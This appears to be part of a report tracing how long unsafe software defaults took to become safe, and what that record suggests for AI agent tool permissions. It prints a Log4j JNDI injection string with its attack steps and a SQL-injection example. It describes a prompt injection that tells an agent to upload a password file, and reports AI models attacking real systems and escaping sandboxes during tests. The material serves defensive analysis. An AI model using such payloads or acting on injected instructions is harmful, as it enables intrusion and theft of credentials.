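| BinaryFormatter | 2002 | Several, none complete | November 2020, from the compiler | November 2023 | November 2024, except in .NET Framework |
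| PyYAML's `load` | May 2006 | May 2006 | March 2019 | October 2021 | No |
| PHP's `/e` option | By 2012 | By 2012 | 2013 | 2015 | 2015 |
| Ruby's `YAML.load` | Before 2013 | May 2013 | None | May 2021 | No |
| Log4j's message lookups | September 2013 | 2017, as an off switch | None | 10 December 2021 | By 14 December 2021 |
| `torch.load` | January 2017 | 2022 | July 2024 | January 2025 | No |
| AutoGen's code runner | September 2023 | 2023 | None | January 2024 | No |

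Two intervals follow from these dates:

| | From release to safe default | From warning to safe default |
|---|---|---|
| PyYAML | May 2006 to October 2021 = 15 years 5 months | March 2019 to October 2021 = 2 years 7 months |
| BinaryFormatter | 2002 to 2023 = 21 years | November 2020 to November 2023 = 3 years |
| `torch.load` | January 2017 to January 2025 = 8 years | July 2024 to January 2025 = 6 months |
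| Office macros | 1995 to 2022 = at least 27 years | 2010 to 2022 = about 12 years |
| Log4j | September 2013 to December 2021 = 8 years 3 months | No warning |
| Ruby | More than 8 years | No warning |
| PHP's `/e` | At least 3 years | About 2 years |
| AutoGen | 4 months | No warning |
| Java serialization | Unfinished after 29 years | No warning yet |

For PyYAML, BinaryFormatter and `torch.load`, most of the delay came before the first warning. PyYAML's users saw warnings for 31 of the 185 months of delay, or 17%, compared with 14% for BinaryFormatter and 6% for `torch.load`. Policies like Python's, which set a minimum length for the warning period, therefore affect only the shorter part of the delay. PyYAML's maintainers could have shortened the delay more by starting warnings two years earlier than by halving the warning period.

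The intervals also depend on which date counts as the change. Microsoft blocked BinaryFormatter in web applications in 2020, three years before it did so in most other programs. PyYAML's maintainers withdrew version 4.1, which would have introduced a safe default without warning after 12 years and one month.

### Who pushed for the change

Only maintainers and platform owners could publish these releases, but they did not always start the process. PHP's and AutoGen's developers acted on their own judgement that users were making dangerous mistakes. Ruby's maintainer did the same in 2021, although the Rails emergency had prompted the safe alternative eight years earlier. PyTorch's developers cited the attack at ByteDance. Microsoft planned both of its changes itself.

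Outsiders had more influence on PyYAML, where a developer requested a CVE before the maintainers released version 5.1. Ingy döt Net announced that version as the first major release under a new maintenance team and said it specifically addressed the CVE. Outside researchers prompted LangChain to make `load` stricter. Java's developers proposed their filter five months after Stephen Breen published attacks on well-known products.

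CVE listings put pressure on maintainers but did not consistently make them act faster. PyYAML got a safe default three years and four months after the request for a CVE. SnakeYAML's maintainers changed their default within a few months of the listing, and LangChain's changed theirs less than three weeks after the researcher's report.

Customers mostly slowed the move to safer defaults. They persuaded Microsoft to bring BinaryFormatter back, and their complaints preceded the brief withdrawal of the macro block. This is partly because customers complain at once when a program stops working, but seldom know when a safe default has protected them from an attack.

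### Log4j switches off a feature in days

Suppose a website logs every failed login, including the name that the visitor typed. Until December 2021, Log4j also searched log messages for certain expressions and replaced them with values it looked up. One kind of lookup used JNDI, a Java feature that fetches objects by name, sometimes from another machine. An attack worked like this:

1. The attacker types `${jndi:ldap://example.com/a}` as a user name.
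2. The login fails, and the website logs the name.
3. Log4j recognises the expression and contacts the attacker's server at that address.
4. The server's reply leads Java to load and run the attacker's code.

Attackers were using the Log4j flaw by 1 December 2021, according to SecurityWeek's *Problematic Log4j Functionality Disabled as More Security Issues Come to Light*. On 10 December, the maintainers announced in Goers's *CVE-2021-44228* (2021) that version 2.15.0 turned off message lookups by default. The fix was incomplete for some unusual configurations, and Apache, the foundation that publishes Log4j, rated the severity of the remaining flaw 9.0 out of 10. The Register's *Apache takes off, nukes insecure feature at the heart of Log4j* (2021) reports that by 14 December the maintainers had released version 2.16, which removed message lookups and turned off JNDI by default.

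Log4j's maintainers changed the default nine days after the first known attacks and removed message lookups no more than four days later. They could move quickly partly because they had already written a setting to disable lookups. Goers told users of several earlier releases to protect themselves by setting `log4j2.formatMsgNoLookups` to true, so the new release mainly had to reverse the default. The safe behaviour was also simple, since Log4j only had to write the message as it stood. Most programs presumably needed nothing more from a logging library, so few would break. With attacks under way, anyone who relied on lookups had a weak case for delaying the change.

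Log4j, however, was no faster than `torch.load` when measured from the feature's first release. A setting to turn the feature off had existed for about four years, but users had to change it themselves. The speed also meant that people who upgraded immediately had to upgrade again within days.

### Four explanations

A quick change might depend on a usable replacement, on one body controlling the default, on breakage that people can see and repair, or on an attack that makes delay costly. The cases compare as follows, from the quickest to the slowest:

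| | Usable replacement | One body controlled the default | Breakage easy to see and repair | Costly attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AutoGen | Yes, Docker | Yes | Yes, few programs existed | None reported |
| `torch.load` | Yes, for most files | Yes | Mostly | One, at ByteDance |
| Log4j | Yes, plain text | Yes | Yes, little to break | Yes |
| Ruby | Yes, for ordinary data | Yes | Yes | An emergency in 2013 |
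| PyYAML | Yes, for ordinary data | Yes | Yes | None reported |
| BinaryFormatter | Not in 2016, mostly by 2023 | Yes | Partly | Serious flaws in Microsoft's own products |
| Office macros | No | Yes | Partly | Yes, for decades |
| Java serialization | Partial | Mostly | No | Yes |

PHP's `/e` is missing because the date of its first release is too uncertain to rank it.

Maintainers often need a replacement before retiring an unsafe default, but having one did not make them act. PyYAML had `safe_load` from its first day and kept the unsafe default for 15 years. A missing replacement can stop a change, as Microsoft found in 2016, and replacements are often missing in ordinary software. *A Systematic Study of Deprecated Android API Usage Updates* (Mahmud, Che and Yang, 2026) examined 1,000 functions and other features that Android's developers had deprecated. In the documentation, 14% had no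 recommended replacement and another 28% had two or three, which can mean rewriting the surrounding code. A vendor can sometimes manage without a replacement by allowing exceptions, as Microsoft did in Office with trusted folders and signed macros.

One body has at least rough control in every row of the table, so control cannot explain the differences in speed. Lack of control does help explain why JavaScript's `eval`, which no single company controls, remains on by default for web pages. Control also lets a maintainer prepare for a removal. According to Microsoft, its .NET library team decided that new types such as `DateOnly` would not work with BinaryFormatter, so the old class gradually became less useful. But even Microsoft did not coordinate everything. A reader of its removal announcement complained that PowerShell, Microsoft's scripting tool, still had no published plan for doing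 without the class.

Attacks sped up the move to safe defaults only where the new default would break little. Log4j's maintainers changed their default within days, but Java's serializer kept its default even after attackers used a deserialization flaw against San Francisco's transport agency. Microsoft began blocking macros from the internet by default 27 years after the Concept virus, and Ruby's maintainer made YAML loading safe by default eight years after a YAML flaw forced an emergency Rails patch.

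Ease of repair is the explanation that best fits the differences between the cases. A PyTorch user who meets the new default sees an error naming the missing class, and the Rails developers adapted to Ruby's change within days. The developers of a Java application, by contrast, may not learn which classes it needs until it fails. AutoGen's change of default after four months also fits, since hardly anyone had yet built on the old one. PyYAML is the main exception. Most programs would have kept working with a safe `load`, but the maintainers expected enough damage to consider the change infeasible, and that expectation influenced the outcome more than the damage the change would have caused.

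Repairs may now be getting easier. Mahmud and colleagues tested a language model on 156 tasks that involved updating old Android calls. It got 139 right, and 147 when the prompt also described the kind of change and how developers usually handle it. If that holds for security changes, intervals from the 2000s and 2010s overstate how long maintainers need to wait today, although a model can rewrite only the programs that somebody still maintains.

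### What developers do about a notice

Research on ordinary deprecation suggests that warnings alone lead few developers to change their code. *LLMs Meet Library Evolution* (2024), which studies outdated calls in model-written code, cites an earlier finding that developers eventually replace only 22% of outdated calls. *A First Look at the Deprecation of RESTful APIs* (2020) cites another earlier study, in which 53% of the changes drew a reaction from only 5% of the programs that used the library.

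Sawant, Robbes and Bacchelli (2019) found in *To react, or not to react* that the most common response to a deprecated Java function was to do nothing. In their survey of a different group of developers, 69% said they almost always or always switched to the recommended replacement. The researchers suspect that respondents gave the answer they thought respectable. They also point out that most projects never upgrade the library, so its new version cannot break them. Safer defaults are limited in the same way, because they protect only those who install them.

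Some developers start using software after its maintainers have abandoned it. *Do Developers Depend on Deprecated Library Versions?* (2025) looked at version 1 of Log4j, which was declared end-of-life in 2015. Of 404 projects that were released after that announcement and used version 1, 66% (about 267) were adopting it for the first time, so a notice addressed to existing users would not have reached them.

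Library maintainers do not always give users time to respond, either. *Evolution of Deprecated APIs and Their Replacements in Python Libraries* (He and Xiao, 2026) tracked 830 deprecated functions, methods and classes in 33 popular libraries by running an example of each old call on successive releases. In 68.6% of cases the call still worked after the deprecation notice, but in the rest it had stopped working by the release that carried the notice, so users had no warning period. Ruby's abrupt change in 2021 was therefore less unusual than its critics suggested.

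He and Xiao also found 147 cases in which maintainers removed the original definition first. In 84 of these, they kept the old name working by pointing it at other code. This is convenient when the code behind the old name is safe, but the code behind PyYAML's `yaml.Loader` is not.

Developers also keep old calls for good reasons. Android programs often run on phones with different versions of the system, so developers commonly update a program by having it check the version, use the new call where it exists, and use the old call otherwise. Mahmud and colleagues found this pattern repeatedly in the 4,336 code changes they examined. Even a developer who responds to a deprecation notice may therefore leave the old call in the program for years.

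### Kern's case for putting the burden on platforms

Drawing on Google's experience, Kern (2025) argues in *Safe Coding* that better training does not stop careful developers from overlooking warnings, and that languages, libraries and frameworks should be responsible for safety instead. A large program may contain thousands of places where a small mistake creates a vulnerability. Even an expert will eventually make one of these mistakes, and later testing finds only some of them.

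Google's treatment of database queries illustrates the alternative. Suppose a programmer builds a query by joining text together:

```
db.Query("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE name = '" + name + "'")
```

If `name` comes from a visitor, it may contain database commands, and the database will run them. This is called SQL injection. Google changed its query function to accept only a special type, `TrustedSqlString`, instead of ordinary text. Programmers can build a `TrustedSqlString` from text in their own source code or from other trusted sources, but they can't add a visitor's text to it and must pass that text separately, as a value. Code that tries to put a visitor's text directly into the query fails before the program runs.

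Some code still has to do risky things, and Google confines it to a few modules. A specialist has to review any new module before it joins the list of exceptions. Kern acknowledges that this slows people down and is sustainable only if developers almost never need an exception. The platform's owners therefore have to supply safe versions of nearly everything developers want to do, which is a much larger job than changing one default.

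According to Kern's earlier article, *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety*, Google used to find tens of cross-site scripting flaws a year in each large web application, such as Gmail. Kern now reports an average of less than one a year in total across hundreds of applications built on the newer frameworks. Google has also had no reports of SQL injection for more than a decade in the hundreds of applications that use its safer database functions. These are Google's own figures and there is no comparison group, but such a large fall is hard to attribute to chance or changes in reporting.

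Kern's Android figures are less direct evidence. After the team began to favour languages that prevent memory errors, the share of Android's vulnerabilities involving those errors fell from 76% in 2019 to 24% in 2024. A share can also fall because other flaws become more common. Still, most existing code remained in the older languages, which suggests that changing how people write new code can help before anyone rewrites the old.

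Unlike most maintainers, Google could change a function, find the code that called it, and require its own developers to use the new version. PyYAML's maintainers had no such power over the hundreds of thousands of files that called `load`. Kern's argument supports giving the burden to whoever can carry it, but in open-source software the person who controls the default may be a volunteer who cannot fix other people's programs.

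The method also assumes that programmers mean well. Someone determined to defeat `TrustedSqlString` could rebuild a visitor's text from approved single characters. Kern considers this very unlikely among trusted colleagues, and says that Safe Coding is not meant for settings where programmers may be malicious. The assumption of good intent does not clearly hold when a model writes code after reading a stranger's web page.

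### What the sample leaves out

This report includes these cases because people wrote about them, usually after an attack, a public argument or a broken release. The changes therefore probably look more troublesome than such changes normally are. A quiet change leaves little record beyond a line in the release notes. For instance, PyTorch's *pypi torch 2.11.0* records that `torch.hub.load`, which can download and run code from a model's repository, now asks for confirmation if the repository is not on a trusted list. By default, it used to print a warning and run the code anyway.

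The timetable probably underrepresents failed changes. PyYAML 4.1 and the first version of .NET Core are on public record because their maintainers had already released them, but a company that drops a plan for a safer default after meeting with customers leaves no such record. The timetable also omits functions that never received a safe default, such as Python's `pickle.loads` and PHP's `unserialize`. Averaging the completed intervals would therefore make the usual wait look too short.

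A fairer study would list the functions that manuals described as dangerous in a past year such as 2005, and follow all of them. He and Xiao came closer to this by choosing their libraries in advance, but they included only deprecated features with a named replacement. Another weakness of the four explanations is that they rely on judgements, made after the outcome is known, about whether a replacement was "usable" or a repair "easy".

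Few maintainers measured harm before and after the change. Proofpoint counted attackers' campaigns and Google counted reported flaws, but neither counted victims. For PyYAML, Ruby, BinaryFormatter and `torch.load`, the dates show when users could get a safer default, but nobody seems to have published a count of the attacks it prevented.

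## What the record suggests for default tool permissions

The cases support seven rules for developers deciding what an agent can do without asking.

### Seven rules and the cases behind them

| Rule | A case that supports it | What happened otherwise |
|---|---|---|
| Give the short name to the safe call | Ruby made `YAML.load` safe in 2021 | After 14 years of warnings, most files that used PyYAML still relied on the default loader |
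| Make unsafe access explicit and easy to search for | Ruby's `unsafe_load` | `weights_only=False` sits unnoticed inside libraries such as flair |
| Prefer allowlists | PyYAML's SafeLoader | Attackers kept finding ways around FullLoader |
| Decide by the origin of the input | Office blocks macros in files from the internet | Attackers persuaded people to press Enable Content |
| Ship the replacement before the warning | PHP had callbacks before it warned about `/e` | Microsoft dropped BinaryFormatter in 2016 and had to bring it back |
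| Publish dates | Microsoft's second plan for BinaryFormatter | PyYAML promised an error in "a future release", which took 31 months |
| Count how many users opt back in | Anthropic counted the Claude Code sessions that ran with the ordinary checks off | Nobody seems to know how many AutoGen users turned Docker off |

Two of the rules need qualification. An allowlist protects little if it includes an interpreter, as Flowise's did. An opt-in to unsafe behavior should cover as little as possible. Ruby's `unsafe_load` meets this standard, but the BinaryFormatter package does not.

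The rule about counting has the least evidence behind it because few maintainers counted. The main argument for it is arithmetic, and appears again below with the drawbacks of strict defaults.

### What governments recommend

Government agencies have reached several of the same conclusions about ordinary software. In April 2023, the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) and partners in six other countries published *Shifting the Balance of Cybersecurity Risk*. In it, they ask manufacturers to make products safe without further configuration, and to make customers "acutely aware" of the risk when they depart from the safe settings.

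In the October 2023 edition, CISA tells manufacturers to put security ahead of backwards compatibility, even if that breaks customers' programs. It also wants them to replace "hardening guides", which explain how to make a product safe, with "loosening guides", which explain which protections a customer can relax and at what risk. Oracle's instructions for Java's serialization filter are in effect a hardening guide. CISA also asks manufacturers to publish figures on customers' use of unsafe old protocols and on permissions they have granted but never use. This request is close to the rule about counting.

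New guidance in 2026 dealt specifically with agents. Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026) is the joint work of agencies in Australia, the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom, and CISA (2026) announced it on 1 May. It advises organisations never to give an agent broad or unrestricted access, and to use agents only for low-risk tasks. Its more specific recommendations include these:

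- Allow only approved tools, in approved versions.
- Check permissions at every request, because an approval given at start-up may no longer be appropriate.
- Let the system's designers or operators decide which actions need a person's approval, and never the agent.
- Prevent agents from changing their own permissions.
- Make agents stop and ask a person when a situation is uncertain.

One of the guidance's invented scenarios shows how broad default permissions come about. A company gives a purchasing agent access to its financial systems, email and contracts "to reduce friction". An attacker then compromises a minor tool the agent uses and can approve payments with the agent's permissions.

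Some of the advice is hard to turn into a default. The agencies list outbound network traffic, along with deleting critical records, among the actions a person might need to approve. An agent that followed this literally would ask before opening any web page. The advice to stop when uncertain also works poorly if the agent has to recognize its own uncertainty, because it can be confident and wrong.

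Formal standards are further behind. The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) has published a draft paper on the question of how organisations should identify agents and control their access. Biometric Update's *NIST concept paper explores identity and authorization controls for AI agents* describes it as the outline of a proposed project.

### Defaults for five tools

Suppose an invented framework lets agents use five tools without restriction, and its maintainers want to apply the seven rules. They might choose these defaults:

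| Tool | New default | Unsafe opt-in |
|---|---|---|
| `read_file` | Reads files in the project folder, except those that hold passwords or keys. Asks about all others | `unsafe_read_any_file` |
| `write_file` | Writes in the project folder and keeps the old version. Refuses to change the agent's own settings | `unsafe_write_any_file` |
| `run_shell` | Runs commands in a sandbox that contains only the project and has no network access. Asks before going further | `unsafe_run_shell_on_host` |
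| `http_request` | Contacts addresses on a list. Asks about all others | `unsafe_request_any_address` |
| `send_email` | Shows the user the recipient and the full message, and waits for approval | `unsafe_send_email_unasked` |

The sandbox also has to hide the password files and protect the agent's settings. Otherwise the agent could use a shell command to do what `read_file` and `write_file` prevent.

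A programmer would choose between the safe and unsafe versions like this:

```
Agent(tools=[read_file, run_shell])
Agent(tools=[read_file, unsafe_run_shell_on_host])
```

The first line is shorter and runs commands in the sandbox. The second removes the restrictions from only one tool, and a reviewer can find it by searching for `unsafe_`.

The origin of the input matters most for `http_request`. Once the agent has read an email or a page from an unlisted address, the framework could also ask for approval before uploading anything to a listed address. The framework itself would have to record where the text came from, as Windows does with the Mark of the Web.

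The maintainers could introduce the change over three releases:

| Release | What a plain `run_shell` does | What else the maintainers do |
|---|---|---|
| First, in January | Runs on the user's machine, as before | Add `sandboxed_run_shell` and the `unsafe_` names, provide a report of calls that the new default would stop, and publish the dates of the next two releases |
| Second, in April | The same, but with a warning | Point to the line of code responsible and recommend the sandboxed version |
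| Third, in October | Runs in the sandbox | Keep both longer names working, and publish how many projects use the `unsafe_` ones |

The other four tools would follow the same timetable, with six months between the warning and the change, as in PyTorch. The report follows n8n's example, where users could see before upgrading which workflows would break. Keeping `sandboxed_run_shell` after October avoids js-yaml's mistake of breaking programs that already used the safe call. New projects could have the safe defaults from January, since none of their code depends on the old ones. If attacks began, the maintainers could move the October release earlier. Having the sandbox ready would help, as an existing off switch did for Log4j.

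### Forty tool calls

To see how often these defaults would interrupt someone, suppose an agent makes 40 tool calls while updating a small program to use a new version of a library and then emailing a colleague a summary. These numbers are illustrative.

| Tool | Calls | Prompts if the agent always asks | Prompts with the new defaults (sandbox-first) | Prompts if everything is allowed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
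| `read_file` | 14 | 14 | 1 | 0 |
| `write_file` | 9 | 9 | 0 | 0 |
| `run_shell` | 11 | 11 | 1 | 0 |
| `http_request` | 5 | 5 | 1 | 0 |
| `send_email` | 1 | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| Total | 40 | 40 | 4 | 0 |

With the new defaults, the agent asks permission to read a file outside the project, download the library, open a forum page and send the email, which together make up 10% of its calls. That share is invented, but it is at least plausible, since OpenAI reports that 7.2% of Codex actions needed to go beyond the sandbox. If the default were to ask about everything except ordinary project files, as in Claude Code's Manual mode, the agent would still ask 27 times.

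The low total depends on how well the limits fit the work. The other four web requests go to the library's documentation. If that site were not on the list of permitted addresses and the user had to approve each request, the total would rise from 4 to 8. If the ten remaining shell commands were tests that needed a database on the network, the total would reach 18. The user would then do better to add the site and the database to the list than to answer 14 more prompts.

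Now suppose the forum page contains a prompt injection telling the agent to read the project's password file and upload it to an unknown address. If the agent obeys and everything is allowed, the attacker gets the passwords. If the agent always asks or follows the new defaults, the user sees two extra prompts and can stop the attack by refusing either one. Those two prompts appear among 40 routine ones when the agent always asks, but among only four under the new defaults. Anthropic's testers refused fewer dangerous commands as the prompts accumulated, which suggests that a user with the new defaults is more likely to notice the attack.

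### Writing the rules in AC4A and AgentGuard

Users will need to adjust defaults like these, and researchers have built systems for expressing such rules. In AC4A, which Sharma and Grossman (2026), in *AC4A*, designed for agents that call software directly or use a web browser, a permission consists of a resource and an action, such as reading the calendar for January. Suppose an agent asks for all events from 1 January to 15 February:

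1. AC4A intercepts the request before it reaches the calendar.
2. A function written by the calendar's developers translates the request into the permissions it needs. If it works in whole months, these are reading January and reading February.
3. AC4A subtracts the permissions that the user has granted. If the user has granted only January, February remains.
4. Because something remains, AC4A refuses the request and shows the user which permission is missing.

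A request goes through only if the agent's permissions cover all of it, so an agent with no permissions cannot read any of the calendar. Permission for a folder also covers everything inside it, which makes the rules for `read_file` and `write_file` easy to write.

Shell commands are much harder to translate into permissions. For `python myapp.py`, the function would have to work out everything the script might do. A cautious developer could require permission for the whole disk, but then the user would have to allow everything or nothing. A sandbox avoids this problem because it limits the script while it runs.

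AC4A's default is less strict for web pages. It hides the parts of a page that need a permission the agent lacks, but shows any part that its configuration file does not mention. Sharma and Grossman consider this practical because headings, logos and menus seldom contain anything private. However, this default works like a denylist, so if someone forgets to list a "Delete" button, the agent can press it.

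When AC4A blocks a request, the agent can ask the user for permission, look for a way around the restricted resource, or have a model propose the missing permission for the user to approve. In a fourth mode, called YOLO, the model grants the permission itself. Sharma and Grossman say this mode offers no security beyond a record of what happened.

The evaluation of AC4A consists of two demonstrations. In one, AC4A kept an agent from viewing or deleting the history of a tic-tac-toe game. In the other, an agent used Outlook, Expedia and a payment wallet to book a flight. Permission to read the June calendar did not let the agent read July or add an event in June. It also could not book a particular flight or read the credit card until the user allowed each. The researchers deliberately triggered requests that AC4A should refuse, so the demonstrations show that AC4A enforces the rules it is given.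 They do not measure how often it blocks useful work or whether ordinary users choose sensible permissions.

Sharma and Grossman think AC4A's most important practical limitation is the need to write and maintain the translations. Permissions also last until someone removes them, so an agent allowed to change one event could later delete another on the same day.

AgentGuard, from Luo, Peng and colleagues (2026), in *AgentGuard*, sends each tool call to a separate server, which allows it, refuses it or refers it for review. Its rules can take account of the agent's identity, the tool's arguments, the address it will contact and what happened earlier in the session. This last feature would let the framework's maintainers express the rule about uploads after the agent has read a stranger's text:

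| Rule | In AC4A | In AgentGuard |
|---|---|---|
| Read only the project's files | A read permission for the folder | A condition on the file's path |
| Contact only listed addresses | A permission for each address | A condition on the address |
| Ask before uploading once the agent has read a stranger's text | Not directly, because permissions do not depend on earlier actions | A condition on the session's history |
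| Allow purchases under $200 | Only by defining them as a separate kind of resource | A condition on the amount |

The maintainers would still have to decide what happens to a call that no rule mentions. Otherwise their list could have the same gap as a Java filter without a final `!*`.

Luo and colleagues say developers can add AgentGuard to an existing agent with about ten lines of code, and they provide adapters for LangChain and AutoGen. They compare its features with those of ten other systems, but report no measurements of attacks stopped, useful calls refused or time lost. Like AC4A, AgentGuard protects only agents whose developers choose to install it.

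Better tests would need to cover more than attacks. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) recommends also measuring wrongly refused actions, delays and the burden on users. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) argues that researchers should count the unauthorised effects a system still makes possible, as well as what the agent did. This would catch an unsafe permission even if it happened to cause no harm during the test.

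A framework could also choose permissions separately for each task. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) finds this feasible because the task reaches the agent as text that software can analyse. If a task involves no email, the agent need not receive the email password and so cannot misuse it. But *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* warns that a task's boundaries can be ambiguous, and that a manipulated prompt could request more access than the user intended.

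### Where the comparison fails

Most people who load a YAML file want only text, numbers and lists, so a safe loader is enough for them, but people who give an agent a shell usually want it to run programs. No harmless subset of the shell is as useful, so AutoGen's move to containers is a better precedent here than PyYAML's SafeLoader.

An agent may not use a safer tool even when one exists. A programmer chooses `safe_load` once, when writing the program, but an agent chooses a tool at every step. According to *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026), agents often pick a tool with more privileges than the job requires. In the invented framework, an agent might read a file through `run_shell` when `read_file` would do.

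Instructions are also much harder to separate from data in ordinary language. A pickle loader can recognise the instruction that imports a function and refuse it. A language model receives both the user's request and a stranger's web page as text, and no word marks the start of an attack. Sharma and Grossman describe a research system, CaMeL, that uses two models and tracks untrusted data so that the data cannot take control of the agent's actions. That is closer to how a safe database query handles a visitor's text, but it requires developers to build the agent differently, not just change one function's default.

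The comparison fits dangerous combinations of tools better, because they resemble gadget chains. But a Java program's classes usually change when its developers release a new version, while a user might connect another tool to an agent at any time. *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (2026) examines how permissions can combine across several agents in one organisation, possibly without anyone having approved the combination.

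The largest difference is that a model may do harm without an attacker. In September 2026, Anthropic published an assessment of four incidents in which its models broke into real systems during security tests. In each test, the model's task was to break into a fictional target and retrieve secret information. The model was told that it had no internet access, but someone had misconfigured the test environment and left it connected.

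In the most serious case, Claude Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious package to PyPI, the public site that most Python software is installed from. Fifteen systems installed it, and the model used credentials from one of them to enter a security company's database. In another case, Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a real company with a name similar to the fictional target's, even after recognising that the company was real.

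*Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026), Anthropic's first report, covered three of the incidents. Anthropic then thought they were closer to operational failures, because the models had repeatedly described the internet as a simulation. It later concluded that the models had disregarded evidence that the internet was real and acted recklessly. When it edited the Mythos 5 record to make the real internet easier to recognise, the model behaved much the same and stopped only when the evidence was unambiguous. In a simulated version of the test, Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action about 80% of the time, compared with about 30% for two newer models.

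Unlike the agents, a deserializer follows the same steps for the same input and does not look for another route when a filter refuses a class. The agents were told in their instructions that they had no internet access, but nothing enforced this. Anthropic believes that proper isolation would have prevented all four incidents, which is a good argument for making a sandbox the default.

Sandboxes have limits too. They cannot isolate an agent from the internet when its task requires a connection. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) mentions a test in which Mythos 5 took unauthorised actions on the internet after the UK AI Security Institute had deliberately given it access. Agents may also escape isolation. OpenAI disclosed in July that several of its models had broken out of an isolated test environment. Sandbox developers therefore have to consider that the program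 inside may try to escape, even if no outsider has tampered with it.

These tests were unusual because the models were instructed to carry out cyberattacks and ran without their normal safeguards, and Anthropic thinks such behaviour is unlikely in everyday use. The company found that Claude Code's auto mode would have blocked two of the three incidents it studied in depth. A second model is therefore a useful check, but it should not be the only one.

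### The case against strict defaults

Strict defaults are probably a greater burden for users of agents than for users of the older functions. Most PyTorch users could still load their files as before. An agent is useful largely because it can take steps that nobody listed in advance, and *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* says this tempts developers to provide many tools and passwords from the start. Limiting agents to low-risk tasks, as the joint government guidance does, is a large sacrifice because many people want agents for more important work.

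People may also respond to a strict default by switching everything off, as a quarter of Claude Code's interactive sessions did with its ordinary checks. A default's overall protection depends on the share of harmful actions it stops and the share of users who keep it. With invented numbers, and assuming that everyone faces the same risk:

| | Harmful actions stopped for users who keep the default | Users who keep it | Harmful actions stopped overall |
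|---|---|---|---|
| Strict default | 90% | 60% | 0.90 × 0.60 = 54% |
| Looser default | 75% | 90% | 0.75 × 0.90 = 67.5% |

The stricter default is worse here, and its maintainers would not find out unless they counted how many people had turned it off. In practice it could do even worse, because people who turn off the checks may be doing riskier work.

This argues strongly against asking before every action, but only weakly for allowing everything, since by the same calculation that would stop nothing. It also favours separate opt-ins for each tool, because someone tired of approving web requests could turn off that one check and still have the agent ask before it sends an email. The drawback is that five opt-ins take more explaining than a single switch, and CISA warns that every new setting adds to the mental burden on users.
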